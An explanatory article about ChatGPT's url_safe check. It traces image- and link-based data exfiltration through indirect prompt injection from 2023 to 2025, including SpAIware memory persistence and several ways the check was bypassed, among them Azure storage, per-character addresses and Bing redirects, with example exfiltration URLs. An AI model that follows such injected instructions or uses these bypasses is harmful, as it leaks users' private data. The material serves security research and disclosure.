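# ChatGPT's url_safe check against data leaks through images and links, and how it was bypassed

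## How an image in a ChatGPT reply can leak a conversation

url_safe is a check that OpenAI added to its chatbot ChatGPT in December 2023. Before the ChatGPT app displays an image or a link from a reply, it can ask url_safe whether the web address is safe, and if the answer is no, the app does not load the image. OpenAI needed such a check because a web address can hold almost any text. If an attacker gets ChatGPT to write private text into an address, and the user's app then requests that address, the attacker receives the text. Security researchers call this data exfiltration: sending a user's private data to an outsider without the user's consent.

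Most of the public record on this leak comes from Johann Rehberger, a security researcher who has published tests of ChatGPT on the blog Embrace The Red since 2023. Roman Samoilenko, a software engineer, found the leak a few days before Rehberger did.

### From a hidden instruction to a server log

Suppose a user mentions a dentist's appointment to ChatGPT and later in the same conversation asks it to summarize a web page. The page's owner has put instructions for the chatbot in it. ChatGPT's language model receives both the user's request and the page as text and can't reliably tell them apart, so it may follow the page's instructions as if the user had typed them.

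In indirect prompt injection, a model processing a web page, file or email for a user obeys instructions hidden in that content. Greshake, Endres and colleagues introduced the term in *Not what you've signed up for* (2023), where they argued that applications built on language models blur the line between data and instructions. They steered Microsoft's Bing Chat with text in a page's HTML comments, which browsers do not display.

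In the dentist example, the hidden lines ask for a picture at the end of the summary. ChatGPT writes its replies in markdown, a way of marking up plain text so that an app can show headings, bold type and so on. A markdown image is a short text code in a reply that the app turns into a picture by requesting it from a web address. The model writes this one:

`![](https://example.com/logo.png?note=dentist-on-Tuesday)`

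The address has three parts that matter here.

| Part | In the example | Use |
|---|---|---|
| Host | example.com | The server that receives the request |
| Path | /logo.png | The file on that server |
| Query string | note=dentist-on-Tuesday | Any further text, placed after the question mark |

The app converts the code into an HTML image tag, and the browser connects to example.com to fetch the logo. Like any browser request, this one includes the path and the query string, so the text about the dentist reaches example.com even if no logo comes back. Websites commonly log the addresses that visitors request, according to OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026), so the owner of example.com can read the text in the log.

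Rehberger printed several real log lines in Embrace The Red's *Advanced Data Exfiltration Techniques with ChatGPT*. One, from 16 September 2023, includes the time, the requested address with the leaked text in its query string (the part after the question mark), and the browser that made the request (Firefox on a Mac). Another from the same day has a query string containing the start of a test chat in which "Alice" says she likes finance and cookies.

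### Why an image needs no click

A browser has to fetch an image before drawing it, so it requests every image as it displays the reply. It requests a link's address only when somebody clicks the link.

The same private text can travel either way. An OpenAI help page, OpenAI's *ChatGPT generated links*, gives an innocent case: a user asks where to buy a car, and ChatGPT, knowing that the user lives in London, offers a link to example.com/car_search/London. Clicking it tells the car site where the user lives. (Here the personal detail is in the path. The query string is the convenient place for leaked text, but any part of the address that the attacker can read back will do.)

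An attacker who relies on a link therefore has to persuade the user to click it. Greshake and colleagues tried this on Bing Chat, with one of them playing a journalist. The chatbot asked friendly questions until it had a name, then offered a link containing a special "code" it said it had made from that name. The injected text had told the chatbot to be persuasive but not how. A wary user can refuse to click a link, but an image loads without a click, and the user can't see it if it is a single transparent pixel.

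This difference between images and links outlasted url_safe. In May 2026 The Hacker News (2026) reported a finding by the firm Permiso Security that ChatGPT still fetched images from a summarised page automatically but showed the page's links as clickable text. A link normally leaks data only if someone clicks it, but messaging apps such as Slack and Telegram fetch a linked page to show a preview. The security firm PromptArmor warns that an AI agent posting into such an app can therefore leak data through a link nobody has clicked.

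### Two failures, and the one that url_safe addresses

The leak requires two separate failures. First, the model obeys text written by an attacker. Then the app sends a request to the attacker's server because the model's reply contained an address. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) describes these failures using two terms from security engineering. An attacker needs a source, meaning a way to influence the system, and a sink, meaning a capability that becomes dangerous in the wrong context.

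The model's obedience is harder to fix than the outgoing request. OpenAI's article says that safety training makes the model refuse in most of the attacks it knows of, but it also describes a 2025 email that worked on ChatGPT in half of the tests. Ordinary software, by contrast, can apply a fixed rule to allow or block an outgoing request every time. The programmer Simon Willison, in *45 posts tagged "exfiltration-attacks"*, argues that the ability to send data out is generally the easiest part of such an attack to remove.

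url_safe works only on the request. Even if it never made a mistake, the hidden lines in the web page would still reach the model, and the model might still obey them in some other way, for instance by giving the user a false summary, which Greshake and colleagues also got Bing Chat to do. Rehberger made the same point about a later version of the check in Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*: it concerns the channel and makes no claim about prompt injection.

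### April to December 2023

In *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version*, Roman Samoilenko imagined a user who copies text from an attacker's website. A script on the site adds instructions to the copied text, and the user pastes it all into ChatGPT without looking closely. ChatGPT then ends its answer with an invisible one-pixel image whose address contains part of the chat. In one test, the address contained login code that ChatGPT had just corrected, including the password "123456". In another, the instructions also applied to later answers, so each new question was sent to Samoilenko's server. Willison (2023) called the method ingenious in a post of the same title on 14 April.

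The attack sometimes failed because ChatGPT can respond differently to the same instructions. Samoilenko found it easy to extract a user's previous questions or code but very difficult to make ChatGPT append passwords or API keys (the codes programs use to log in to online services). A slow reply could also reveal the attack. Samoilenko still thought OpenAI should stop ChatGPT from replying with markdown images.

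Rehberger independently found the same behaviour in early April and reported it to OpenAI on 9 April 2023. OpenAI had no bug bounty programme then, so he and the company discussed it by email. According to Rehberger's *ChatGPT Plugins*, OpenAI replied that displaying these images was a feature and that it planned no changes.

For the clipboard attack alone, that answer was defensible. Samoilenko had written that the method did not exploit a vulnerability as such, and agreed that users are responsible for what they paste. But OpenAI was adding plugins, extensions that let ChatGPT read web pages and use other services, and Rehberger had warned the company that these would let an attacker do the same thing remotely. *ChatGPT Plugins* demonstrates such an attack. A plugin fetches a malicious page, and ChatGPT obeys the text in it and leaks a summary of the earlier conversation through an image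 address. The summary includes the string "TooManySecrets123", which the user had typed before the plugin fetched the page. The user pastes nothing and has no chance to inspect the page's text before ChatGPT reads it.

Each new ChatGPT feature gave Rehberger another demonstration. Custom instructions let a user save text that ChatGPT applies to every exchange. In Embrace The Red's *ChatGPT Custom Instructions*, the saved text makes ChatGPT end each reply with an image whose address summarises the latest message and answer, so the leak repeats at every turn. Rehberger compared it to the forwarding rule that an intruder leaves behind in a victim's email account. The comparison is apt, and it also marks the limit of the demonstration: somebody has to get the text into the settings first. (ChatGPT's later memory feature gave attackers another way to make a leak persist.)

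By September, Rehberger had a way to avoid having to fit a long chat into a web address. The injected instructions made ChatGPT use a plugin to write the conversation into a document, diagram or video on an outside service, so the image only had to leak the address of that file. Rehberger sent OpenAI a draft of the write-up on 23 September and got an automated response.

The last demonstration before the fix used a custom GPT, a version of ChatGPT that any paying user could set up with their own instructions and share. Rehberger's GPT, called The Thief, offered a game of tic-tac-toe but first asked for an email address to personalise the game and a password as part of a "security process", SecurityWeek reported. A hidden image sent the user's answers to Rehberger's server. OpenAI screened GPTs before publication and blocked the first version, whose instructions contained words such as "steal"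 and "malicious". The GPT passed the screening after Rehberger reworded its instructions.

According to Embrace The Red's *Malicious ChatGPT Agents*, Rehberger reported The Thief on 13 November 2023, and OpenAI closed the ticket two days later as "Not Applicable". OpenAI did not answer two follow-up messages, and Rehberger published on 12 December. The model was following the instructions of the GPT's own builder, as OpenAI had designed it to do, so the attack involved no indirect prompt injection. A model that ignored every hidden instruction on the web would still have leaked the password, which is a good reason to check the request itself.

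The Thief still worked when Rehberger showed it live to a consenting victim. By the next day, ChatGPT's web app had begun to check image addresses, according to Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*.

### Content Security Policy and the Bing Chat fix

Other companies had acted sooner than OpenAI. Rehberger reported the same leak in Bing Chat to Microsoft on 8 April 2023, a day before the report to OpenAI, and Microsoft fixed it within about two months. (Rehberger's later account dates the fix to May; Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat* says word of it came on 15 June.) The fix relied at least partly on a Content Security Policy, a website's published rule for which hosts the browser may load images and other resources from.

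The browser receives the policy together with the web page and enforces it. *Content Security Policy Level 3* (2026), a draft from W3C, which maintains the standard, defines a directive called img-src that controls images. If a page's policy allows images only from example.com and the page requests one from example.org, the browser refuses to fetch it. In Bing Chat, the model could still obey a malicious page and write the markdown image, but the browser never sent the request. Microsoft's policy allowed images from four hosts, all belonging to Bing: th.bing.com, www.bing.com, edgeservices.bing.com and r.bing.com. Rehberger's earlier attacks stopped working, though Microsoft may have made other changes that an outsider could not see.

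Such a policy protects users only if the hosts it lists are safe. The standard lets an entry specify a host and a path but not a query string, so private text can go to any address that the policy allows. Google's chatbot Bard was vulnerable in this way in September 2023, because its policy allowed images from anywhere under google.com, and Google lets the public run small programs on one of those hosts. In Embrace The Red's *Hacking Google Bard*, Rehberger used such a program to record the leaked text. Google confirmed a fix a month after the report, without changing the policy. Similar mistakes have recurred since. Willison describes a policy at the software company Salesforce that still allowed a domain whose registration had lapsed, so researchers could register it. Microsoft's short list of its own hosts was much safer than Google's or Salesforce's policy.

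By contrast, Anthropic changed its chatbot Claude in July 2023 so that it loaded markdown images only after the user clicked "Show Image", according to Embrace The Red's *Anthropic Claude Data Exfiltration Vulnerability Fixed*. In effect, this made images as safe as links. By November, Rehberger's slides in *New Important Instructions* (2023) listed Bing Chat, Claude, Bard and three other products as fixed, and ChatGPT as "won't fix".

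OpenAI could have adopted a strict policy like Microsoft's, which would have closed the image route in ChatGPT's web version and let anyone read what was allowed. It would also have blocked harmless images from the rest of the web. This drawback had grown since April, because more and more plugins relied on ChatGPT displaying outside images, and Rehberger had warned that the fix would get harder the longer OpenAI waited. OpenAI has not said whether this is why it didn't adopt such a policy. The check it introduced in December allowed some outside images and blocked others, and OpenAI did not publish the rule for deciding which.

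## What url_safe checked, and which apps used it

Rehberger found url_safe by looking at what ChatGPT's web app did with a reply that contained an image. The app had started to make an extra request before displaying the picture. Applied to the dentist example, the exchange that Embrace The Red describes would go like this:

1. OpenAI's server sends the reply, which includes a markdown image with the address `https://example.com/logo.png?note=dentist-on-Tuesday`.
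2. The web app holds the image back and sends its address to url_safe, a service on OpenAI's own servers. The request also contains the conversation's identifier.
3. url_safe answers `{"safe":false}` or `{"safe":true}`.
4. If the answer is false, the app leaves the image out and never contacts example.com. If it is true, the browser fetches the image as before.

In Rehberger's test, the URL contained an email address, and url_safe rejected the URL. In the second step, the user's browser sends the private text to OpenAI, which already has the conversation.

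The web app checked links too. In early January 2024, people who built custom GPTs began complaining on OpenAI's developer forum about links that looked normal but did nothing. A user wrote in *Hyperlinks in Custom GPT not linking?* that the text was blue and changed colour under the mouse. The address behind it was missing because the app had checked the link with url_safe, received "false" and removed the address. Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT url_safe Mechanism Bypass* (2025), an advisory from a security company, confirms that the check ran on images, hyperlinks and other kinds of link.

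Links were less dangerous than images but caused most of the complaints. One builder's GPT produced reports too long for the chat and gave the user a link to each one. After the change, the builder could only ask people to copy the address into a new tab, and complained in *Custom GPT Bug* that the fix did more harm than good. Pasting an address sends the website the same text as clicking the link, but the user at least sees the address first and has to make some effort.

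### A hidden rule instead of a published list

Outsiders could study url_safe only by submitting addresses and noting the results, whereas anyone could read the Content Security Policy that Microsoft used for Bing Chat. Rehberger asked OpenAI to publish the details of url_safe, partly because he worried that it might be just another language model. He was still asking in 2025, when Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection* recommended a public list of the domains that url_safe trusted.

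The secrecy also made ordinary faults hard to diagnose. When a policy blocks an image, the browser's developer console shows which rule blocked it, but the GPT builders saw only the word "false". One suspected that links longer than about 15 characters failed, and another blamed brackets in the address. Some of the trouble came from bugs that OpenAI then fixed.

But url_safe was more flexible than a policy. It checked the query string, so it could accept `example.com/logo.png` and reject the same URL with a note about a dentist added there. It could also cover links, which a policy's image rule doesn't.

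The check also gave OpenAI a central record of every address that the web app was about to display, so the company could look for patterns that suggested an attack. A browser can report requests that violate a website's security policy, but it doesn't report the requests that the policy allows. Rehberger considered the central record a benefit and hoped that business customers would be able to set stricter rules for their own staff.

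Simon Willison, who linked to the Embrace The Red post on 21 December 2023, was glad that OpenAI had finally done something but found the fix "a bit weird" and "half-baked". He thought the obvious alternative was to block all images from outside domains. He expected that a creative attacker would get data past the filter, perhaps by hiding it in subdomains or filenames. Later tests of the rule showed that OpenAI had thought of subdomains.

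### What outsiders inferred about the rule

Rehberger first guessed that ChatGPT might look images up in the index of Microsoft's search engine, Bing. Such a check would accept addresses already on the web and reject any that the model had just composed to include someone's private text. He had little to test this with. On his server, url_safe accepted `a.png` but rejected `d.png` in the same folder. Rehberger couldn't say why, and none of the later tests explain it.

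The security company Imperva got further in 2024 by sending text straight to the service. According to Imperva's *From ChatBot To SpyBot*, url_safe took everything the user had supplied, including custom instructions, and accepted an address if that exact run of characters occurred anywhere in it. The characters didn't even have to form a valid web address. (Imperva also prints the rule as a line of code, but the line lacks a minus sign and would accept almost anything.)

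Such a rule is sound in principle, because the model can't have added anything private to an address that was in the conversation before it began its reply.

Imperva also found that a bare domain, with nothing after it, passed even if nobody had mentioned it. A new subdomain (the part in front of the domain, as in `news.example.com`) normally failed. According to Imperva, this is because a domain's owner can create subdomains freely and use them to carry data, whereas each new domain costs money. However, any subdomain of google.com passed, as did any path or query string on openai.com. A trusted host is a domain whose addresses the check accepts even when the rest of the address is new.

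Suppose that a user has typed `https://example.com/photos/cat.png?size=large` and no other address. Imperva's rule would then give these answers:

| Address in ChatGPT's reply | Relation to what the user typed | Answer |
|---|---|---|
| `https://example.com/photos/cat.png?size=large` | Exact match | Safe |
| `https://example.com/photos/ca` | Shortened match | Safe |
| `https://example.com/photos/cat.png?size=dentist` | Changed query string | Not safe |
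| `https://example.org` | Bare domain, never mentioned | Safe |
| `https://dentist.example.com` | New subdomain | Not safe |

The shortened address passes because it appears as one unbroken string in the address the user typed. It passes even if no file with that name exists.

Several of other people's observations fit this rule. In the forum thread *BUG report*, a user posted an error message from url_safe about a failure to load the conversation. The service would not need to load the conversation if it checked only the address. In early February 2024, an OpenAI employee told builders in *Hyperlinks in Custom GPT not linking?* that links worked badly when the model constructed a full address itself or filled in details, and that their own software should return the complete address to ChatGPT instead. Builders would have to do this if the check compared the model's output with text already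 in the chat.

A developer's test in *Can not open generated hyperlinks in desktop browser* shows that the rule also blocked harmless links. The developer had made a small website that turned questions and answers in a query string into flashcards, so that ChatGPT could create a set of cards by writing a link. url_safe accepted the bare page but rejected the same page with a query string about the chemical symbol for water and the capital of Japan. Nothing in those flashcards was private, but a text comparison can't distinguish a harmless address composed by the model from one that contains a stolen password.

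Gregory Schwartzman, a computer scientist in Japan, found much the same behaviour in ChatGPT's browsing tool, which opens web pages from OpenAI's servers. In *Exfiltration of personal information from ChatGPT via prompt injection* (2024), he reports that ChatGPT would open an address written out in the prompt but refused when asked to replace part of it with the user's age. It would also open shortened versions of an address in the prompt. He and Imperva tested different routes for getting data out of ChatGPT, so their agreement on such an odd detail is good evidence that OpenAI was comparing text on both routes.

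Tenable's *HackedGPT*, published in November 2025 after research mostly on the GPT-4o model, gives a looser description. It lists four things that url_safe took into account:

- whether it trusted the domain
- whether there was a subdomain, and whether it trusted that
- the same two questions about parameters, meaning the contents of the query string
- the context of the conversation

This is compatible with Imperva's findings but doesn't say how the service weighed one factor against another, and Tenable presents the list as incomplete.

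It is unclear whose text counted as part of the conversation. Imperva put its test addresses in custom instructions, and Schwartzman put his in text that the user pasted. Both count as the user's own input, even if an attacker wrote them. The OpenAI employee's advice implies that data returned by a GPT's outside service counted too. If the text of any web page that ChatGPT had read also counted, an attacker could get an address approved by putting it on the page. In Embrace The Red in 2026, Rehberger described a narrower rule as he understood it, in which an address that the user entered directly was safe for the rest of that chat.

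### The apps that never asked

url_safe was a client-side check, which means that the user's app had to request the answer and obey it. An app without that code had no protection, however good the rule was. In December 2023 only the web app had the code. Rehberger looked at the iPhone app, version 1.2023.347, and found no sign of it. He assumed that the Android app was in the same position.

The forum complaints support him, and they come from people who weren't looking for a security hole. Links that didn't work in a browser opened normally in the iOS and Android apps, according to *URLs served by action/GPT not clickable in desktop*. One of the first people to complain said that links failed on mobile too, but most found that they worked. The flashcard developer, whose link also worked on a phone, naturally assumed that the desktop block was the bug.

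Rehberger guessed that OpenAI left the checking to the client to keep replies streaming quickly. ChatGPT shows a reply piece by piece while the model is still writing, and a server that did the checking would have to hold back part of the reply until an address was complete and checked. The browser log in *BUG report* fits this guess. It shows a new url_safe request each time another piece of an address arrived, and users in the thread saw links appear during the writing and vanish afterwards.

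Rehberger thought OpenAI should check on the server anyway. If the server removed an unsafe address before sending the reply, every app would benefit, including old versions that people hadn't updated. A Content Security Policy would not have filled this gap, because a phone app that draws its own replies has no web page for the policy to govern. A server-side check would have cost a short delay in replies with links or images, and that seems a small price considering what happened next. (In 2025 Rehberger noticed that the web app's calls to url_safe were no longer visible.)

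OpenAI opened its next app, for macOS, to all users of recent Macs on 25 June 2024, after offering it only to some paying subscribers, as reported in SiliconANGLE's *OpenAI launches ChatGPT app for Mac* (2024). The url_safe check was six months old by then, but this app did not use it either, according to Rehberger's *Trust No AI* (2024), a paper that collects his attacks on several companies' products.

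Rehberger has also written that the Android app shipped with the same flaw, though he wrongly dates its release to 2024. SiliconANGLE's *OpenAI launches Android version of its ChatGPT app* (2023) puts the launch on 25 July 2023, about five months before url_safe appeared. So OpenAI had left an existing Android app unprotected, whereas it built the new macOS app without a protection it already had.

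### SpAIware

Memory, a feature OpenAI began introducing in February 2024, made the macOS omission much more serious. ChatGPT saves notes about a user, such as a name or a preference, and adds them to the model's input at the start of every later chat. The model can save a note without the user requesting or confirming it.

In May 2024 Rehberger showed in Embrace The Red's *ChatGPT: Hacking Memories with Prompt Injection* that an outsider could write these notes in three ways. When a user referred to a shared Google document, ChatGPT followed instructions in it and saved each bullet point as a separate memory. Instructions in an uploaded image also worked. Web pages were harder because ChatGPT read the injected text but at first refused to use the memory tool. Rehberger had to use indirect methods, which worked only some of the time. The only warning to the user was a small "Memory updated"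 notice above the reply.

OpenAI closed the report as a "Model Safety Issue", not a security vulnerability. Rehberger objected that this had nothing to do with model safety, because outsiders could now alter data stored in a user's account and influence all future conversations. OpenAI's label is easier to understand for the report alone, since a false memory does not itself send data to anyone. Rehberger had not yet published what a memory could do in an app that fetched any image it was given.

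He sent OpenAI that demonstration in June. Embrace The Red's *Spyware Injection Into Your ChatGPT's Long-Term Memory (SpAIware)* goes through it step by step:

1. A user of the macOS app asks ChatGPT to read a web page or document that an attacker has prepared.
2. Hidden instructions make ChatGPT save a memory. It tells the model to add an image to its future replies and to put the conversation into the query string of the image's address.
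3. The user starts a new chat about something else. ChatGPT loads the memory together with all the others and follows it.
4. The macOS app requests the image without consulting url_safe, and the attacker's server logs what the user typed and what ChatGPT answered.

The last two steps repeat in every later conversation, and the image can be invisible. Rehberger's custom instructions demonstration also persisted across conversations, but this time an attacker didn't need access to the user's settings.

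The attack worked because the macOS app never ran the url_safe check. The address in step 4 has a new query string on an unknown site, and url_safe had rejected that kind of address in Rehberger's first test. The missing check also undid much of the protection in the other apps, because memories belong to an account rather than a device. An instruction that someone picked up in the protected web app would presumably have started to leak data once they opened the Mac app.

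The wording on Rehberger's test page stopped working sometime in July, and he found other wording that worked. OpenAI closed the leak in September 2024 with version 1.2024.247 of the macOS app, and Rehberger presented the attack at a security conference on 20 September. The iOS app got url_safe at about the same time, about nine months after the web app, according to Embrace The Red's *AI Domination*.

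The fix stopped the image request, but a page or document could still plant a memory. The Hacker News pointed out that deleting a chat does not delete the memories saved from it, so a memory planted before the update would have stayed in the account. Rehberger advised users to review their stored memories regularly or use temporary chats, which don't draw on memory. In November 2025, Tenable reported that text on a web page could still get ChatGPT to update its memories.

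## How researchers got data past the check

By late September 2024 ChatGPT's web, macOS and iOS apps all used url_safe, so an attacker needed addresses that the check would accept. Researchers found two ways to get them.

Suppose an attacker wants to know the day of the user's dentist appointment. The hidden instructions can make ChatGPT write "dentist-on-Tuesday" into an address on a trusted host, where url_safe accepts any text after the domain. Or the attacker can prepare seven addresses, from `example.com/monday` to `example.com/sunday`, and have ChatGPT load the one that matches the appointment. None contains anything private, but the owner of example.com learns the day by seeing which one was loaded.

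### Private text in an address on a trusted host

Rehberger reported several bypasses to OpenAI in early October 2024, soon after the macOS fix, and presented the work at the Black Hat Europe security conference that December. The talk took SpAIware a step further. A planted memory made ChatGPT open a page on GitHub, a site where programmers share code, at the start of each conversation and follow the instructions there. The attacker could then give a hijacked account new orders at any time. (ChatGPT kept copies of pages it had already opened, so the memory included a counter that pointed to a fresh page each time.)

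url_safe accepted GitHub, so the orders could come in, but the attacker couldn't use GitHub to get data out. ChatGPT could request a GitHub address containing private text, but only Microsoft, which owns GitHub, can read the server's logs. Embrace The Red therefore lists three requirements for a leak: url_safe accepts the site, the site takes data through the kind of request that loads an image, and the attacker can see what arrived.

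Azure Blob Storage, a Microsoft service that rents out file storage, met all three. Its files have addresses under windows.net, which url_safe accepted, and the customer can read a log of requests for them. Rehberger had already found at least one other such site, but Azure was the easiest to demonstrate. He later named apache.org as a second accepted domain whose logs he could read.

| Host in the image's address | url_safe's answer | Who can read the requests |
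|---|---|---|
| An unknown site with private text in the query string | Not safe | The site's owner |
| GitHub | Safe | Microsoft |
| Azure Blob Storage | Safe | The customer renting the space |

Microsoft runs both of the accepted services, but only Azure can be used to leak data, because it passes the record of requests on to its customers and anyone can become a customer. Google's policy for Bard had the same weakness. A list of reputable domains is therefore a poor guide to safety wherever a company rents out space under its own name.

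The form of Azure addresses made this worse because each customer's storage account has its own subdomain of windows.net. In Imperva's tests, url_safe normally rejected new subdomains, but it evidently made an exception for those of windows.net, even though they may belong to unrelated customers. OpenAI has not explained the exception, but many ordinary websites keep their pictures on Azure, and rejecting them all would have led to more complaints like those on the developer forum.

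Rehberger returned to the problem in 2025 and was surprised that some of the October 2024 bypasses still worked. By then ChatGPT had a chat history feature, which put material from the user's recent conversations into the system prompt, the text the model receives before the user's first message. In the demonstration on Embrace The Red, a malicious PDF made ChatGPT copy that material into the address of an image on Rehberger's Azure account. SpAIware had leaked only the messages and replies sent after the infection, but this attack also leaked material from conversations that had ended before the user opened the PDF.

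Rehberger asked OpenAI about a fix several times in the month before he published the demonstration, but received no update. He left out the injected text.

### AgentFlayer

In August 2025 the security company Zenity used Azure storage to steal data from a user's Google Drive. ChatGPT had a new feature called Connectors, which let it search a user's accounts on services such as Google Drive, SharePoint and GitHub. The OECD's AI incident monitor has an entry dated 6 August, *ChatGPT Connectors Vulnerability Enables Zero-Click Data Theft via Poisoned Documents* (2025).

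In Zenity Labs' *AgentFlayer*, a user uploads a document and asks for a summary. Tiny white text in the document tells ChatGPT to instead search the connected Drive for API keys and put them in an image address. The text also includes a story about a developer with a deadline, because ChatGPT is otherwise less likely to handle keys.

Zenity's first attempt failed because url_safe rejected the image address, which pointed to a test server on a service that gives out temporary addresses. The researchers then used an image on Azure storage, again with the keys as parameters in the address, and the keys appeared in their log. The model followed the document's instructions both times, so whether the keys leaked depended on whether url_safe accepted the host.

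Zenity credits Rehberger with the image route but presents the Azure bypass as its own discovery. Rehberger had already described that bypass publicly, which makes Zenity's discovery weaker evidence that the gap was easy to find. It does confirm that the gap was real and exposed more than chats.

According to The Decoder's *An invisible prompt in a Google Doc made ChatGPT access data*, the attack could extract only small amounts of data, not whole documents. That limit does little to protect an API key, which is short and may give access to an entire account.

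OpenAI paid a bounty of $1,111. *Pwn the Enterprise*, a newsletter post about Zenity's conference talk, lists the attack as fixed, by which it means that the injected text no longer works. That text told the model a story about a deadline. A different story might still work, and the Azure address would then be as useful for leaking data as before.

### One address per character

Removing every trusted host from the list would have stopped these attacks, but an attacker can also use addresses that contain no private text. Rehberger tried this in December 2023, on the day he discovered url_safe. He gave each letter and digit its own image on his server, 36 in all, so that the sequence of requests would spell out the data. url_safe let ChatGPT display nine of the images, which was enough for Rehberger to leak the word "hi" in two requests.

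Embrace The Red conceded at the time that the method was slow, leaked very little and was easier for a user to notice. OpenAI could notice it too if it monitored url_safe, since one reply would produce a string of nearly identical checks. The leaked text could also contain errors. A browser keeps a copy of an image it has loaded and may not request it again, so "hello" could reach the server as "helo". Requests can also arrive out of order, which would scramble the letters.

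Imperva built on the idea in 2024. Since url_safe accepted any address already in the user's text, the attacker only had to put the whole list of addresses there. In Imperva's scenario, the attacker first breaks into an account through a flaw in ChatGPT's website. The stolen login token expires after about two and a half days, but anything the attacker has added to the custom instructions stays. Those instructions can leak a password whenever the user types one, so it matters less that the leak is slow.

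Custom instructions had room for only 3,000 characters, and Imperva compared three ways of fitting an alphabet into them.

- **A list of addresses.** Each character has its own entry, such as `example.com/a` and `example.com/b`. The list takes up a lot of the space, so a short domain name helps.
- **One long address, cut short.** The instructions contain only `example.com/abcdefghijklmnopqrstuvwxyz`. To send a "d", ChatGPT requests `example.com/abcd`, which passes as a shortened match. This saves space, but ChatGPT takes longer on average to write the addresses.
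- **One domain per character.** url_safe accepted any bare domain, so the instructions need only describe how the names are formed. This was the fastest method and took the least space.

Imperva says an attacker needs 32 domains, but covering 26 letters and ten digits takes 36, which would cost $36 to $72 at one or two dollars each. Imperva guessed that OpenAI accepted bare domains because of this cost. If so, OpenAI underestimated what a thief would pay for someone's passwords.

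Imperva still thought OpenAI was moving in the right direction. An attacker could get around the check, but consistently extracting large amounts of data without being detected had become much harder.

### Schwartzman's age and postal code tests

Schwartzman used fixed addresses with ChatGPT's browsing tool. His attack starts with a user who pastes a long piece of program code into ChatGPT without noticing the instructions inside it. The instructions list several addresses, one for each age range, and ask ChatGPT to open the one that fits the user:

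`example.com/under10`
`example.com/10to20`
`example.com/20to30`

ChatGPT opened the matching page, and the server recorded the user's age range. The user doesn't have to state an age, since the model can infer one from a remark about graduating from high school that day. If ChatGPT has no useful information yet, an attacker can use one injection to instruct it to save any hint about the user's age to memory, and a second injection a month later to collect the answer. An attacker who can inject instructions several times can also narrow down a number by repeatedly halving the range.

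A postal code has too many possible values for a list like this. Schwartzman instead made use of shortened addresses, which ChatGPT would also open. He supplied one long address for each digit and let the length of the shortened version stand for the digit, plus one so that a zero still left a character. To send the code 302, ChatGPT would open these pages:

| Address in the pasted text | Digit | Address that ChatGPT opens |
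|---|---|---|
| `example.com/aaaaaaaaaa` | 3 | `example.com/aaaa` |
| `example.com/bbbbbbbbbb` | 0 | `example.com/b` |
| `example.com/cccccccccc` | 2 | `example.com/ccc` |

Each digit needs its own address because ChatGPT would not open the same address twice, which Schwartzman attributes to caching. The attacker can also use the different first letters to put the digits in order if the requests arrive out of sequence.

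The model was bad at this kind of counting and opened the wrong addresses. Schwartzman fixed this by including a short program in the pasted text, which ChatGPT ran to work out the list of shortened addresses. Running the program slowed the attack, giving the user more time to notice and stop it. ChatGPT also opened at most ten addresses per prompt, which limited the leak to ten characters.

These experiments did not test url_safe's handling of images. Schwartzman writes that the same techniques can be used with images, and thanks Rehberger for pointing this out. Imperva's tests of url_safe support his main point. The limit of ten applied to pages the browsing tool opened, so it can't be used to infer how many images a reply could contain.

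OpenAI judged Schwartzman's report "non applicable". MITRE, an American organisation that assigns reference numbers to software vulnerabilities, found the report interesting but could not assign a number because the flaw was in a web application that customers don't control. IPA, a Japanese agency, said it could do nothing because OpenAI's terms of use make users responsible for what goes into ChatGPT and what comes out. Someone who has pasted hundreds of lines of code would struggle to meet that standard.

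### Bing's redirect links

Tenable's researchers combined a trusted host with fixed addresses. They noticed that url_safe always accepted bing.com. Bing's search results link to addresses on bing.com, which redirect the browser to the listed sites. Every site in Bing's index, including an attacker's, therefore has an address that url_safe would accept. Imperva had warned in 2024 that such a redirect on a trusted domain might defeat the check.

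One such link is enough for phishing, because ChatGPT shows the user an approved link that leads to a malicious page. Leaking data takes more work because nobody can add private text to Bing's links. Tenable got a separate page into Bing's index for each letter of the alphabet. To leak "Hello", ChatGPT displays the Bing links for H, E, L, L and O in turn, and each request reaches the attacker's page for that letter.

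Tenable still had to get its instructions to a model with access to private data. According to Tenable, ChatGPT used a second model to read web pages, and that model couldn't see the user's memories or earlier messages. A malicious blog comment could take over the second model, but that model had no private data to leak. Tenable made the second model end its summary with further instructions, which ChatGPT read as part of the conversation when the user sent another message. A display bug hid these instructions from the user. ChatGPT then loaded the images through Bing. Tenable also got this version of the attack to work with GPT-5.

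Tenable reported the Bing links to OpenAI on 10 December 2024, and OpenAI acknowledged the report the same day. Tenable asked for updates six times between then and 4 March 2025. According to the timeline in Tenable's advisory, OpenAI's only reply was to add another person to the conversation. The problem was still unresolved when the advisory came out. In November, Tenable said it had worked with OpenAI to fix some of the problems it had found, but didn't say whether this was one of them.

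### Speed, visibility and amount

| Method | Requests | What the user might notice | Data in the demonstration |
|---|---|---|---|
| Private text on a trusted host | One | Nothing, if the image is a transparent pixel | API keys, recent chat history |
| One image address per character | One per character | Several images and a slow reply | The word "hi" |
| One page per age range | One | A small box saying that ChatGPT opened a page | An age range |
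| One shortened address per digit | One per digit, up to ten per prompt | The same box and a longer wait | A postal code |
| One Bing link per letter | One per letter | Several images or links | Private text, letter by letter |

Writing text into an address on a trusted host was the most dangerous method while it worked. It was fast and almost invisible, and a single request could hold more than the other methods could send in a whole reply. But it depended on OpenAI trusting a particular domain, so OpenAI could stop it by changing one entry. Leaking data through fixed addresses suits short answers such as passwords and ages, and is much harder to stop because each request looks like an ordinary page visit.

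### Rehberger's recommendations and OpenAI's fix

Rehberger suggested in 2023 that ChatGPT should display only one image per reply, or a handful at most. With a limit of one, an eight-character password would take eight replies to leak. The limit would also restrict users who want many images in one reply, and it would not have stopped the Azure attacks, which needed only one image.

His advice to publish the list of trusted domains addresses those attacks better. Someone who knew how Azure storage works could have spotted the problem with windows.net at once. Publishing the list would also help attackers, but Rehberger, Zenity and Tenable all found usable hosts without it. Rehberger also wanted configurable settings for business customers, which would have let a company that didn't need images from windows.net block them without waiting for OpenAI.

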